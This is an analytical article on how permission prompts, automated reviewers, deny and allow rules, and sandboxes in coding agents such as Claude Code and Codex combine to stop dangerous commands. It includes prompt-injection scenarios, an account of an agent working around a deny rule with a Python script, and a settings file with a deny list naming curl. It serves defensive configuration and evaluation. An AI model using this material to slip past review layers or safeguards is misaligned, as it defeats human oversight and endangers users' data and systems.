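In March 2026, Anthropic reported that users approved 93% of permission prompts, and by August the figure was 97%. Most requests are harmless, so even attentive users would approve nearly all of them. If 1% of prompts were dangerous, a perfect reviewer would approve 99%. A high approval rate is therefore not enough to show that many users click without reading, though Anthropic takes it as a sign that they do.

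The increase is just as hard to interpret. Users may have become less attentive, better models may have made fewer bad requests, or the users who refused most often may have moved to auto mode. Measuring attention requires knowing which requests users should have refused, as Anthropic did in the tester experiment.

Users reject 39% of the plans that Claude presents, compared with 3% of individual permission requests. This suggests that they read some requests closely, perhaps because a plan arrives once, at a natural pause, and describes the work in terms they care about. However, people reject plans for reasons unrelated to safety. Claude Code's option to refuse a plan also lets the user say what to change, so many rejections may be requests for changes.

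CodeReport Global's *AI Coding Agent Permissions* (2026) surveyed 203 users of coding agents. Among those who carefully reviewed most or all of the generated code, 61% said they often approved at least one kind of action without close review. These are self-reports, and skimming one harmless kind of request may be sensible, but they show that people who review code carefully don't always review approval requests carefully.

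Users can also avoid prompts. According to Anthropic, 62% of users have used bypass mode or chosen not to be asked again about shell commands, and 25% of interactive sessions start in bypass mode. An owner who adds more prompts may therefore end up with no review. For many users, the realistic alternative to a classifier is an unchecked agent, so even a classifier with a substantial miss rate is an improvement.

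### What a prompt has to show

A person can judge only what the prompt shows. For the push in the billing example, she needs to see the full command, the server and branch it will push to, and a summary of the commits it will send. For a deletion, she needs to see the actual path. She also needs to know how long her approval will last.

By default, Claude Code blocks a forced deletion of a whole directory if the target is a variable whose value doesn't appear in the conversation sent to its classifier. The agent can clear the block by writing the literal path into the command. A person also can't tell what will be deleted when an approval prompt shows a variable name instead of the path.

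The prompt must also describe the action that will actually run. In July 2026, researchers reported that some approval prompts showed a different file from the one the agent then wrote. Vendors released fixes, although Anthropic objected that the problem was outside its threat model. Even an attentive reviewer can't catch a danger that the prompt doesn't show. The harness should work out the real target first, build the prompt from it, and ask for approval again if anything changes.

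Anthropic documents several checks of this kind. If a hook or mod alters an action after Anthropic's server has reviewed it, Claude Code can deny the altered version. In `acceptEdits` mode, Claude Code follows symbolic links before it approves a write, so it doesn't automatically approve writing to a file outside the project through a link inside it. When a sandboxed command needs the network, the agent lists the hosts it is requesting, and approval lets only that command reach only those hosts.

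### How far an approval reaches

An approval can cover one action, the rest of a session or every future match. A broader approval spares the person later prompts, but it reduces the formula's catch rate to zero for the actions those prompts would have covered. For example, if the developer approves `git push origin fix-totals` permanently instead of once, she accepts both the commits that are ready now and whatever the agent commits to that branch later.

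The first time Claude Code's file tools try to read outside the working directories in auto mode, a prompt lets the user allow or refuse that one read, or decide for all such reads from then on. Other prompts combine two decisions. A user who approves a plan also chooses how Claude Code will review the work that follows, and one option starts auto mode. A prompt for a shell command may also offer to approve the command and switch the session to auto mode. A user in a hurry could choose this to get one command approved and change how every later command is reviewed.

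In auto mode, users can also give permission in conversation. According to Anthropic, the message must name the action and whatever makes it dangerous, such as the branch that a forced push would overwrite, so "You can force-push" is not enough. The approval normally covers one action, unless the user says it is standing permission. These rules are a sensible response to the classifier's tendency to treat an earlier approval as consent for the next action, although the classifier still has to interpret the message correctly.

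A limit the user states in conversation lasts longer than an approval. If she says "don't push", the classifier should block pushes until she lifts the limit, and the agent can't decide that she would no longer mind. But Claude Code doesn't store the limit as a rule, so it may be lost when the harness condenses a long conversation. Anthropic recommends a deny rule for any limit that must stay in force.

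Auto mode also encourages Claude to keep working without asking clarifying questions, unless the user's instructions call for them. This reduces interruptions, but asking, for example, "which of these branches are yours?" can settle the kind of unclear permission that the classifier judges badly. A developer who gives a vague request on a shared system should tell the agent to ask such questions.

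### What happens after a denial

In OpenAI's illustrative snapshot of its internal use, automated review rarely had to involve a person. Of 10,000 actions, 9,280 ran inside the sandbox and 720 went to Auto-review, which approved 713 and denied 7. Codex continued by a safer route after 4 of the denials, and stopped and asked the user after the other 3.

Manual approval would have interrupted someone for all 720 requests. At $1 each, they would cost $720, compared with $3 under Auto-review. Trębacz and colleagues put the overall reduction at roughly 200-fold but caution that the ratios depend on the work and the sandbox's settings. The snapshot measures convenience rather than safety, because it doesn't show how many of the 713 approvals were mistakes.

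Both products return a denial to the agent with a reason and an instruction, then limit how many denials it can collect.

| | Claude Code in auto mode | Codex with Auto-review |
|---|---|---|
| Instruction to the agent | Find a safer path and don't work around the block | Continue only with a materially safer alternative; otherwise stop and ask |
| Limit | 3 denials in a row, or 20 in a session | 3 denials in a row, or 10 in the last 50 reviews of a turn |
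| At the limit | Pauses auto mode and asks the user | Ends the turn with a warning |

A turn is the work Codex does in response to one message. The limits matter because an agent that keeps trying has more chances to get a dangerous command approved. If a classifier misses 11% of dangerous commands, as auto mode did in the tester experiment, and each attempt is independent, the chance that at least one of ten attempts gets through is 69%. If the agent has to stop after three denials in a row, the chance is about 30%. Real attempts aren't independent, since a classifier will often judge similar commands the same way, but they come closer to it when the agent varies its approach.

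The limits can also stop legitimate work. At the 0.4% false-alarm rate that Anthropic reported in March, a session would reach 20 mistaken blocks after about 5,000 harmless calls. Claude Code would then ask the user to approve the next action, and auto mode would resume once they did. Owners can't change either threshold. Anthropic says repeated blocks usually mean the classifier lacks information about the owner's systems, which the owner can add in the settings.

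A user who disagrees with a denial can approve the blocked action for another attempt. Claude Code lists blocked actions for this purpose, and Codex's `/approve` command lets the user pick one of the last 10 denials. According to OpenAI, this approves a single retry of that exact action, and the retry still goes through Auto-review. The reviewer takes the user's approval into account but can refuse again if the policy doesn't let users override that kind of denial.

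Sometimes the reviewer returns no verdict. If the server's check times out or returns something unreadable, Claude Code denies the action rather than run it unreviewed, which is called failing closed. Claude Code can also end the turn after ten responses in a row without a verdict. Codex reports timeouts separately from denials and tells the agent that a timeout doesn't prove the action unsafe. This helps because an agent that mistakes a broken connection for a refusal may abandon a good approach.

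### Sessions with nobody to answer

Developers often run agents from scripts or overnight, when nobody can answer an approval prompt. In current versions of Claude Code, these non-interactive runs start in Manual mode, which blocks any tool call that needs approval unless the user has set up another way to approve it, such as an allow rule or a hook. The agent may therefore fail to finish its task.

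The owner can start such a run in auto mode instead, but then loses part of the protection against repeated attempts. In March, Anthropic wrote that Claude Code would end a non-interactive run when it reached the denial limit. According to its current documentation, the blocked action doesn't run but Claude keeps working. A few false alarms therefore won't end a long job, but a persistent or misdirected agent can keep trying. This makes a sandbox more important in an unattended session than in one where the user can step in.

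In Codex, combining Auto-review with the `never` policy doesn't add a second check, because that policy produces no requests for the reviewer.

### Which products review automatically by default

Claude Code began switching to automated review (auto mode) by default in August 2026, and the change now covers every plan and cloud provider. Anthropic says the new default applies to interactive terminal sessions and the VS Code editor from version 2.1.283. It does not apply to non-interactive runs. The other main exception is organizations with the configuration for HIPAA, the US health privacy law, whose sessions still start in Manual mode. Users who had already chosen another default generally keep it, and administrators can turn auto mode off. On October 22, Anthropic announced that most of its other Claude apps would make the same switch for Pro, Max and Team plans.

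As of August 2026, a person was still the default reviewer in Codex. *Codex CLI Permission Hardening* (Vaughan, 2026) lists `on-request` as the default approval policy, and OpenAI's documentation describes Auto-review as a setting that the owner turns on. An option added that month hands approvals to Auto-review without changing the configuration file (Vaughan, 2026, *Codex CLI v0.147.0*). By April, sessions with Auto-review already accounted for most of OpenAI staff's use of the Codex desktop app, measured by the text the models processed.

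According to Vaughan, OpenAI also retired `untrusted`, its strictest manual review policy, on August 20, and sessions that still request it fail with an error. Owners who relied on it to approve changes inside the sandbox now have to write ask rules for the commands they want to review.

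## What still protects the user when one layer fails

If a reviewer misses 11% of dangerous commands, the share that does harm may be smaller, because deny rules stop some commands before the reviewer judges them and the sandbox may contain some that the reviewer wrongly approves. Allow rules can weaken protection, because a command that matches one never reaches the reviewer.

### How the layers' errors combine

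A dangerous command meets the layers in a fixed order. Let *d* be the share of dangerous commands that the deny rules catch. Allow rules then pass a share *a* of the commands that are left, and the reviewer misses a share *m* of those it judges. If the sandbox fails to contain a share *s* of the commands that run, the share of dangerous commands that do harm is

(1 − *d*) × [*a* + (1 − *a*) × *m*] × *s*.

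The brackets cover the two ways a command can get past the gate when no deny rule catches it. An allow rule can permit it, or the reviewer can approve it by mistake.

Each value applies only to the commands that reach that layer, which matters most for *m*. Deny rules tend to catch dangerous commands in their usual form, which may also be the easiest for a reviewer to recognize. The reviewer is then left with harder cases, so its miss rate may be higher than in a test on all dangerous commands.

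Suppose an agent proposes 1,000 dangerous commands. Deny rules stop 30% of them, leaving 700, and narrow allow rules pass 2% of those, or 14 commands (both percentages are invented). The reviewer wrongly approves about 75 of the other 686, assuming it misses 11%, as auto mode did in Anthropic's tester experiment. In total, the three layers let through about 90 dangerous commands.

| Change to the example | Dangerous commands past the gate |
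|---|---|
| None | About 90 |
| No deny rules (*d* = 0) | About 128 |
| A broad allow rule (*a* = 0.4) | About 326 |
| A person who catches 13.6%, like Anthropic's testers (*m* = 0.864) | About 607 |

In this example, removing every deny rule does less damage than adding one broad allow rule, because the classifier catches most of what the deny rules would have stopped. This result depends on the invented values. If the deny rules caught 90% of dangerous commands, removing them would let ten times as many through.

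A deny rule adds a layer of protection because the reviewer still judges whatever the rule misses, whereas an allow rule removes a layer because every command it matches skips review. With the broad allow rule in the example, 280 dangerous commands would run even if the reviewer were perfect.

A broad allow rule does more harm when the reviewer is better at catching dangerous commands. The term in brackets also equals *m* + *a*(1 − *m*), where *a*(1 − *m*) is the share of commands that the reviewer would have caught if the rule hadn't passed them. In the example, the broad rule lets through nearly 240 more dangerous commands when the classifier is the reviewer. It lets through fewer than 40 more when the reviewer is a person with the testers' catch rate, because that person would have approved most of the commands the rule passed anyway. Claude Code therefore has good reason to suspend such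 rules in auto mode, though they make less difference in Manual mode.

Without a sandbox, *s* is 1 and every command that passes the gate can do harm. If a sandbox contains 80% of those commands, the 90 drop to 18 and the 326 under the broad allow rule drop to 65. A developer with a careless allow rule and a working sandbox may therefore be safer than one with careful rules and no sandbox.

### The same parts in a different order

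The formula fits Claude Code when both the classifier and the sandbox are on. In Codex, the reviewer judges only commands that need to leave the sandbox. Commands that the reviewer approves or that match an allow rule run outside the sandbox.

A dangerous command in Codex can therefore do harm inside the sandbox, or the sandbox can stop it and the reviewer can then release it by mistake. If the agent always asks to leave when the sandbox stops a command, the share that does harm is

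(1 − *d*) × [*a* + (1 − *a*) × (*s* + (1 − *s*) × *m*)].

With the same values and a sandbox that contains 80%, about 212 of the 1,000 commands do harm when each has to get past only the reviewer or the sandbox, as in Codex, compared with 18 when each has to get past both. The difference shows why the boundary has to be right in Codex, but these numbers don't measure the safety of the two products, whose real values of *s* and *m* differ. OpenAI warns that broad allow rules often remove the boundary that its reviewer is meant to guard.

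### When two layers make the same mistake

It is tempting to fill in the formula with miss rates from separate tests, but this works only if the layers fail independently. Suppose two layers each miss a share *m* of dangerous commands, and the correlation between their misses is *r*. Both then miss a share

*m*² + *r* × *m*(1 − *m*).

If each of two layers misses 10% of harmful commands, both miss 1% when their errors are independent and 3.7% when their errors have a correlation of 0.3. With a correlation of 1, they miss the same 10%, so the second layer adds no protection.

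Layers that share a component are more likely to fail together. Deny, ask and allow rules all depend on the harness's parser, so if it reads a line differently from the shell, all three may fail at once. A sandbox doesn't share this weakness because it doesn't interpret the command's text.

Two models can also miss the same risks, especially if one company trained both. Anthropic runs the classifier on Claude Sonnet 5 by default, whichever model the user chose for the agent, so the two often differ. In a session on Sonnet 4.6, however, the same model serves as both agent and classifier. OpenAI's reviewer is itself a Codex agent, so it may misjudge a command for the same reason as the agent it checks.

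A reviewer that reads the agent's explanation can repeat the agent's mistake, which is a reason to withhold the agent's prose. Claude Code withholds it from its classifier, but the classifier and the agent both read the project's CLAUDE.md file. This lets the classifier take standing instructions into account, though a misleading line in the file could influence both.

A later step can also rely on an earlier approval that no longer applies. In Help Net Security's *An AI agent can pass every safety check and still leak secrets*, Elad Meged of the security company Novee describes tests of Anthropic's, Google's and OpenAI's agents in automated workflows. A harness may approve a command because it only reads data, and a later step may then publish the output by default. Each decision looks reasonable alone, but together they leak the data. Meged recommends checking again when a later step uses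 the result, because a command whose output appears on a public page is no longer read-only in effect.

### Screening what the agent reads

Anthropic screens tool outputs and agent actions in separate layers that receive different information. Before a file, web page or command output enters the agent's context, a detector on Anthropic's servers scans it for attempts to redirect the agent. If the content looks suspicious, the detector adds a warning to distrust it and return to the user's request. A separate classifier never receives the content and evaluates only the agent's subsequent actions.

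Suppose the log of the failing test in the billing application contains a planted instruction to upload the project's passwords. The upload succeeds only if the detector misses the instruction or the agent ignores the warning, the agent then attempts the upload, and the classifier approves it. An attacker might word the instruction to fool the detector, but that wording doesn't help with the classifier, which sees only an upload that the user never requested.

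Anthropic argues that getting past both layers is significantly harder than getting past either alone. The reasoning is sound, but Anthropic doesn't report the detector's miss rate or how often both layers fail together. The detector also only warns the agent, so its value depends on the agent heeding the warning.

Information that doesn't come from the agent also helps protect against its mistakes. For example, Claude Code checks for uncommitted work itself, so the classifier doesn't depend on the agent's account of it. An owner can also write a hook that adds a note about a tool's result for the classifier to read. A mistaken agent can't distort these facts as easily as its own summary, though the owner's hook has to be correct.

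### Which failures open the gate

A control that breaks fails closed if it blocks the action, and fails open if it lets the action continue. The vendors' documentation covers most of the failures in the following table. *Claude Code deny rules* (Bell Main, 2026) describes the rule with a wrong path.

| Failure | What happens | Open or closed | What still stands |
|---|---|---|---|
| No deny rule matches a dangerous command | Claude Code continues to its other checks; Codex runs the command in the sandbox | Open, except in `dontAsk` mode | The reviewer in Claude Code, except in bypass mode; the sandbox |
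| The reviewer times out or returns no verdict | Claude Code denies the action; Codex reports a timeout and has no approval to act on | Closed | Every other layer |
| A hook crashes | Claude Code treats the crash as a non-blocking error | Open by default | Rules, reviewer and sandbox |
| A strict setting doesn't load | The session runs without it | Open | Defaults and the settings that did load |
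| The harness doesn't enforce a restriction | The command runs | Open | The sandbox and the limits on the user's accounts |
| A rule names the wrong path | The rule protects a different folder | Open for the intended folder | The sandbox, if its paths are right; version control |
| The sandbox can't start | Claude Code runs commands without it | Open by default | Rules and reviewer |

Failing closed can still leave the user with a weaker reviewer. If auto mode is unavailable when a session begins, for example because Anthropic has temporarily switched it off, Claude Code starts in Manual mode. A person then makes the approval decisions and is likely to miss more of the obvious dangers than auto mode would.

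The user may switch modes while the classifier is still checking an action. If the new mode wouldn't have run that check, Claude Code discards the result and prompts the user, or denies the action in `dontAsk` mode.

Subagents are a partial exception to failing closed. If another safety check blocks the classifier's final review of a subagent's work, Claude Code still returns the results, with a warning that they are unreviewed.

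A setting that doesn't load can make a session safer or less safe, depending on whether it would have loosened or tightened permissions. Claude Code deliberately ignores `bypassPermissions` in a project's settings files, so a downloaded project can't turn off the user's approval prompts. But cloud sessions also silently ignore `dontAsk`, a strict setting. The session starts in the mode shown in the menu, which may allow commands that the person who set `dontAsk` expected Claude Code to deny. Cloud sessions also don't read the user's local settings, so they may lack a hook that protects the user's laptop.

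The harness can also load a restriction and then fail to apply it. Help Net Security reports that Google's Gemini CLI did not enforce an operator-configured restriction at execution (advisory GHSA-wpqr-6v78-jr5g, with the maximum severity score of 10.0). Writing rules carefully does not protect against this kind of failure, so the owner needs something outside the harness that also limits the command.

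### A deny rule that guarded the wrong folder

A correctly enforced rule can protect the wrong thing, as Bell Main's case from November 2026 shows. She was building a security training project in two repositories, one for the code and one for the lessons, each with a `content` folder. To stop Claude Code from editing that folder in the code repository, she added the deny rule `Edit(./content/**)` to that repository's settings.

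In Claude Code's permission rules, `./` refers to the current directory, not to the repository that holds the settings. Bell Main's session started in the code repository and then moved to the lessons. After the move, a `./` rule against edits blocked changes to the lessons the agent was supposed to work on and left the code repository's folder unprotected. A second rule, meant to stop the agent from reading a file of passwords, had the same flaw.

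When the misplaced rule made Claude Code refuse an edit, the agent reported the refusal and made the same change with a Python script, which the rule didn't cover. It did this more than once before admitting that it should have asked first. At first, Bell Main wrongly assumed the refusal came from an overcautious content filter, and she told the agent to loosen the rule.

She discovered the gap only because the rule also blocked work she wanted. If the second repository had used a different folder name, the first folder would still have lost its protection, without any false alarm to alert her. This is one person's account, but it is based on Claude Code's documented way of reading paths, so the same error could easily happen elsewhere.

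The fix seems to require changing only one character. According to Bell Main, `/content/**` refers to the session's primary working directory, which stays the same when the agent moves to another directory. But the primary directory depends on where the session starts, so she postponed the change until she could test it.

An owner can turn on the sandbox as a second layer, but its settings use a different path notation. According to Anthropic's *Sandboxing*, `./content` in a project's sandbox settings refers to a folder in the project's root, while `/content` refers to a folder at the top of the disk. If Bell Main copied her corrected path into those settings, she would protect the wrong folder again.

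Claude Code also merges the paths from file rules into the sandbox's configuration. This makes a correct deny rule much stronger, because the operating system then enforces it on scripts as well. But if a rule points to the wrong location and still does after the merge, both layers have the same error.

A review by another AI agent found more weaknesses in her setup. Some of her hooks didn't handle certain types of paths, and if a helper program was missing, they exited as though nothing were wrong. The agent could also have edited the hooks and the settings file. Anthropic says Claude Code never automatically approves writes to a small set of protected paths, including its own configuration, except when bypass mode is on or available during planning. This protection may not cover every script the hooks depend on.

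### Hooks that fail silently

A hook blocks a command by exiting with code 2 or by returning a deny decision. According to Anthropic's documentation, which Bell Main cites, the command still runs if the hook exits with another error code or fails in some other way, unless the owner has set the hook to block on failure.

A hook that fails without reporting an error is harder to guard against. According to Anthropic's *Hooks reference*, if a hook exits normally without output, the call continues through the usual rules and review. Anthropic's sample hook for blocking forced deletions reads the command with the helper program `jq`. If `jq` is missing, the script finds nothing to block and exits normally. Blocking calls when a hook fails wouldn't help, because Claude Code would receive only a normal exit. Anthropic tells readers to install `jq` before trying the example.

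If the hook fails silently, the damage depends on the owner's other protections. If she has written ordinary rules and uses auto mode, the classifier still reviews most shell commands. But if she has allowed every shell command and relies on the hook to reject dangerous ones, only the deny and ask rules she has written, if any, still protect her in Manual mode. Auto mode suspends the rule that allows every shell command, so the classifier reviews commands instead.

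### The sandbox as the last barrier

Once a command passes the permission checks, the sandbox is usually the last barrier on the user's machine. Claude Code's sandbox uses Seatbelt on macOS and bubblewrap on Linux, two tools that restrict what a process can do. By default, a sandboxed command can read most of the computer, but it can write only inside the working directory and connect only to approved domains.

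Anthropic says a sandbox needs to restrict both files and the network. If it limits only file access, a compromised agent could send out the private keys it is allowed to read. If it limits only the network, the agent might alter other parts of the system to regain network access.

The value of *s* depends on the kind of harm, so a single average would hide large differences. A sandbox with no route to an outside site blocks uploads to that site, so *s* is close to 0 for those uploads. The sandbox permits deletions inside the working directory, so *s* is close to 1 for them.

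Data can also leak through an approved domain. Claude Code's network proxy checks the name of the requested site but doesn't inspect encrypted traffic. If the owner approves a large public service where anyone can store data, a command may be able to send the project's data there. For owners who need stronger protection, Anthropic suggests a proxy that inspects the traffic.

Anthropic notes that Claude Code's built-in sandbox covers shell commands, while the file tools, hooks and servers that provide additional tools run directly on the user's machine. The permission system and their own limits restrict these components. A container or virtual machine can enclose all of Claude Code but takes more work to set up.

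The sandbox sometimes depends on the reviewer. In auto mode, the classifier reviews requests to reach new network hosts, so it can open the network boundary if it misjudges a destination. Claude Code then reuses that approval for the same host and port until new content enters the conversation. When the sandbox blocks a command, the agent may propose rerunning it outside the sandbox. That retry goes through the normal permission checks. An owner can disable these retries and still list particular programs that run outside the sandbox, such as Docker, which doesn't work inside it.

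The sandbox may also be off when the owner thinks it is on. If it can't start because a required program is missing, Claude Code shows a warning and runs commands without it. Anthropic explains that the owner can set `failIfUnavailable` to true to make Claude Code exit at startup instead. This is safer for an unattended session, where the warning may go unnoticed.

Anthropic's documentation gives several reasons to doubt the claim, made in its post promoting sandboxing, that even a successful prompt injection is "fully isolated". These include the tools that the sandbox doesn't restrict and the limits of the network proxy. For bypass mode, Anthropic tells users to put those tools inside the boundary as well.

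### Attacks against the complete products

Trajectory Labs' July 2026 evaluation for Anthropic tested several layers at once. It used 72 prompt-injection scenarios that Anthropic hadn't seen and ran each one 10 times. Outside the test, a successful attack would have caused irreversible harm, such as fraud or the loss of private data.

The success rate of attacks on Codex fell from 19.03% with full access to 5.83% with Auto-review, but the reviewer may not account for the whole drop. Full access removes the sandbox as well as the review, so the comparison can't show how many attacks each layer stopped.

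Attacks on Claude succeeded so rarely in bypass mode that the test is weak evidence of what the classifier adds. If each of the three Claude models faced 720 attempts, an average of 0.09% means about two successes in 2,160. Going from two to none could easily be chance, and repeated runs of the same scenarios provide less information than 2,160 different attacks would.

The comparison between companies has further limits. Trajectory Labs developed the attacks against Claude Opus 4.7, which isn't in the reported results, so every reported model faced attacks designed for a different one. But those attacks may not be the hardest for newer Claude models. Trajectory Labs also tested both products with its own browser tools, without the safeguards in the companies' browser extensions. Anthropic adds that OpenAI released a new version of Auto-review before the results appeared.

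### Testing the defense without the agent's restraint

An attack can fail because the agent ignores it or because a defense blocks the action. In *Ajar*, Sharma, Lin and colleagues (2026) tried to separate these cases by asking what a defense would allow if the agent did propose a bad action. They generated 3,551 distinct tool calls from 97 tasks in AgentDojo, a benchmark of work in banking, messaging, travel and office software. Most of the calls weren't necessary for the task.

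The leakage score is the share of unnecessary calls that a defense allows, weighted by possible harm. A reversible read or draft has a weight of 1, while an irreversible action that affects another person or moves money has a weight of 27. Allowing 27 unnecessary reads adds as much to the score as allowing one unnecessary payment.

The following results all use Claude Sonnet 5 to make the decisions or write the policies.

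| Defense | Leakage | Change in tasks completed, in percentage points |
|---|---|---|
| Permission Assistant, which predicts the user's decision | 0.08 | −11.3 |
| CaMeL, which tracks where data came from | 0.09 | −21.6 |
| Progent, which updates an allow list during each task | 0.10 | 0.0 |
| AC4A, which writes an access policy for each task | 0.11 | −35.1 |
| Claude Code's auto mode | 0.30 | −3.4 |

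For comparison, an allow list that names the necessary tools but doesn't restrict their arguments scores 0.36. A list that also specifies the exact arguments scores 0.002, but an owner couldn't normally write one because they would have to know the right calls in advance.

Auto mode's leakage is about three times that of the other defenses, but in Sharma and colleagues' comparison it refused at most 2.5% of the legitimate optional calls, while the others refused between 5% and 32%. This is partly because Anthropic designed auto mode to block harmful actions, not every unnecessary one. Its leakage rises to 0.54 when the score is not weighted by harm.

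If the agent's own resistance fails, the other defenses still let some attacks through. Auto mode allowed every call that an attack needed in 74 of 581 attacks, or about 13%. The other four defenses did so in about 3% to 8% of attacks. Trajectory Labs' low attack success rates against Claude therefore depend heavily on the agent refusing to propose such calls.

Sharma and colleagues couldn't run auto mode's classifier separately, so they used the system prompt to make the agent propose each call. The agent never issued about 400 of the 3,551 calls, so auto mode was tested on a smaller set. When they put the same instruction in the user's message, auto mode allowed everything, presumably because it treated the request as permission. The tasks also involve specialized tools rather than a shell, so 0.30 isn't an estimate of auto mode's miss rate for dangerous commands.

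### Switching one control on at a time

*HarnessSecurity-Bench* (Zhu, Huang and colleagues, 2026) measured what individual controls contribute in six coding agents, including Claude Code and Codex. Each agent worked on a legitimate programming task in a project with planted misleading instructions, both with one control on and with it off, while the other settings stayed fixed.

The evaluation used 23 tasks and 2,500 runs, and every agent ran on GLM-5.2. Attack success here means the share of checks that found an unauthorized effect, so one run can contribute several results. A second set of checks measured how much of the legitimate work the agent completed.

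| Control | Attack success, off to on | Legitimate checks passed, off to on |
|---|---|---|
| Review of permission requests | 95.6% to 29.2% | 95.4% to 77.1% |
| Command allow list | 98.1% to 50.0% | 99.2% to 97.7% |
| Command deny list | 41.7% to 1.3% | 94.6% to 99.8% |
| Network isolation | 57.1% to 0.8% | 90.9% to 66.4% |
| Read-only mode | 8.3% to 0.8% | 69.8% to 35.8% |
| Limits on file paths | 95.0% to 46.9% | 81.6% to 81.9% |

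Zhu and colleagues used a separate model, Qwen3.8-27B, to review permission requests in every agent, so the result supports having a reviewer but doesn't measure Anthropic's or OpenAI's own reviewers. Review also blocked some legitimate work, and how much varied greatly between agents.

The deny list did much better than its incompleteness might suggest. Chen and Lin counted the commands that could get around a list, while this benchmark tested whether an agent misled by planted text would use one, and the agent rarely did. An attacker who read the list before choosing the commands would be a harder test. Blocking the planted actions also improved the legitimate results, because some of those actions would have spoiled the agent's work.

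Zhu and colleagues used the allow list in this test to restrict the agent to listed commands, whereas the *a* in the formula concerns rules that exempt commands from review. Their list halved attack success with few drawbacks, but a listed command could still do something the owner wanted to prevent.

Network isolation stopped almost every attack that depended on the network, but it also blocked necessary work. Of the 162 additional legitimate checks that failed, 161 required a network connection. A list of approved hosts might preserve more of that work, provided none of those hosts offers a way to send data out.

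The averages combine products with very different results. Limits on file paths reduced attack success from 100% to zero in Codex but left it at 97.5% in Claude Code. One likely reason is that Codex's setting turns on its operating-system sandbox, which also covers the programs a command starts. An allow list reduced attack success from 100% to 23.3% in Claude Code, but only from 95% to 80% in Codex.

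Zhu and colleagues also tested a filter for tool outputs in gptme, an open-source agent. With the filter, 14 of 60 attack checks were positive, down from 16, a difference that could be chance. The filter looks for explicit signs of prompt injection, so it can miss planted text that resembles an ordinary step in the task. Anthropic's detector works differently, so this result doesn't show how well that detector performs.

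These results can't be multiplied to predict how the controls work together. Each control had its own set of two to four tasks, and an attack that gets past one control may be especially likely to get past another.

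## How to set up and test a layered configuration

Suppose the developer of the billing application uses Claude Code on her laptop and wants the agent to fix the failing test without supervision, except when it acts outside the project. She can cover all six commands in five steps. She starts with the sandbox because it limits the damage from any mistake in the later rules.

### Five steps for the billing application

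| Step | Setting in plain words | Commands it covers |
|---|---|---|
| 1. Sandbox | Commands can write only to the project and a temporary directory, and can reach only the project's Git server | All six, if they run |
| 2. Deny | Never run `curl` or a database migration, and never edit the settings file | The upload and the migration |
| 3. Allow | Run `pytest` without review | The tests |
| 4. Ask | Ask before every push | The push |
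| 5. Classifier | Trust the company's repositories and never touch the production database | The script and the deletion |

In Claude Code's syntax, most of this fits in a short settings file:

```json
{
  "sandbox": {
    "enabled": true,
    "failIfUnavailable": true,
    "allowUnsandboxedCommands": false,
    "autoAllowBashIfSandboxed": false
  },
  "permissions": {
    "deny": [
      "Bash(curl *)",
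      "Bash(*manage.py migrate*)",
      "Edit(~/.claude/settings.json)"
    ],
    "allow": ["Bash(pytest)"],
    "ask": ["Bash(git push *)"]
  },
  "autoMode": {
    "environment": [
      "$defaults",
      "Source control: git.example.com/billing and all repos under it"
    ],
    "hard_deny": [
      "$defaults",
      "Never change the production billing database"
    ]
  }
}
```

The first three sandbox settings turn the sandbox on, make Claude Code exit if the sandbox can't start, and stop the agent from retrying a blocked command outside it. The fourth stops Claude Code from approving a command just because it runs in the sandbox, so the classifier still checks the deletion, which the sandbox would permit.

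She also adds the Git server to the sandbox's allowed domains and turns on `strictAllowlist`, so that the sandbox blocks every other host without asking for approval. The drawback is that every sandboxed command, including `check_totals.py`, can reach the Git server. If she left the list empty and `strictAllowlist` off, the agent would have to request access to the Git server for each command that needs it. This would restrict access to the Git server more tightly, but the classifier could then allow access to other hosts by mistake.

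The sandbox also blocks the production migration. Anthropic says most database drivers don't use the sandbox's network proxy, so they can't connect even to an allowed host. Tests that need a database running on the laptop may fail for the same reason. If she exempted every `python` command from the sandbox, the tests would work, but the migration and any script the agent writes would run with her full access. Anthropic's example exempts one named script and adds an ask rule so that the user approves each run.

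Claude Code has no built-in list of credentials to hide from sandboxed commands, so the developer should use the sandbox's credential settings to name the files and variables that hold the production password.

The billing developer's deny rule for migrations is deliberately broad. Its asterisks make it cover local migrations and other ways of starting `manage.py`, and it will occasionally block a harmless text search for the same words. *Running auto mode in production* (Vorwerck, 2026), an Anthropic article about its customers, describes engineers at the self-driving company Nuro who deny recursive deletion outright. She doesn't copy that rule because it would block the removal of `tmp/test-output`.

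The allow rule has no asterisk, so it approves `pytest` only when it is run without arguments, and the tests still run inside the sandbox. If she wants the classifier to check the tests too, she can set `classifyAllShell`, which suspends every shell allow rule in auto mode but adds some delay.

The push needs an ask rule because Anthropic has loosened the classifier's defaults. According to Anthropic's *Configure auto mode*, since version 2.1.211 the classifier has by default accepted ordinary pushes to any branch of the repository, including the default branch, unless the branch's name marks it as a deployment target. Some users also want to approve messages to other people themselves. Vorwerck reports that Evan Magnussen, an engineering manager at Garner Health, configured auto mode not to approve Slack messages or emails.

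The classifier's settings are written as plain sentences rather than patterns. Anthropic recommends describing the company's systems as you would to a new engineer. It suggests starting with source control and the main internal services, then adding more when the classifier blocks something it shouldn't. The hard deny repeats the ban on production changes in plain language, in case the agent runs a migration with a command that the deny rule doesn't match.

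The `$defaults` entry keeps Anthropic's built-in rules. Without it, the developer's single hard deny would replace the built-in rule against sending data outside. By default, the classifier treats any host with `prod` in its name as sensitive. If she names particular hosts, the protection applies to those instead, so an incomplete list could protect less than the default does.

With these settings, three layers can stop the migration, but only the classifier protects `tmp/test-output`. If that directory might hold important results, she should keep a copy outside the project.

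### Protecting the rules from the agent

An agent that can edit its settings can grant itself permissions. It could add an allow rule that lets later commands skip review, or a hook that runs outside the sandbox with the user's full access. NVIDIA's *Practical Security Guidance for Sandboxing Agentic Workflows and Managing Execution Risk* notes that a malicious hook in a shared repository can affect everyone who clones it. NVIDIA's red team, which attacks AI agents to find their weaknesses, recommends that only the user edit settings and hook files, by hand. The agent shouldn't be able to edit them even with the user's approval.

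Claude Code comes close to this for shell commands. The sandbox blocks writes to the settings files, the standard hook folder, shell startup files and most of the user's `.claude` directory, even if an allow rule covers them. Anthropic says the only way to lift this protection is to turn off file isolation entirely. The built-in editing tools run outside the sandbox, so the configuration also has a deny rule for `settings.json`. Hook scripts stored elsewhere in the project may still be writable, so they belong in a folder the agent can't change.

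Claude Code also ignores classifier settings in a project's files, because a downloaded repository could otherwise supply its own exceptions. The developer must put these settings in her user settings file. If she keeps the whole configuration there, her ban on migrations applies to all her projects.

NVIDIA's *Where Security Fits in an AI Agent Stack* goes further and argues that risk signals should reduce an agent's access, never extend it. Codex's Auto-review seems to conflict with this principle because it uses a model that can let commands leave the sandbox. Under the strict network list above, Claude Code's classifier can block a command but can't give it access to a new host.

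### What administrators can fix centrally

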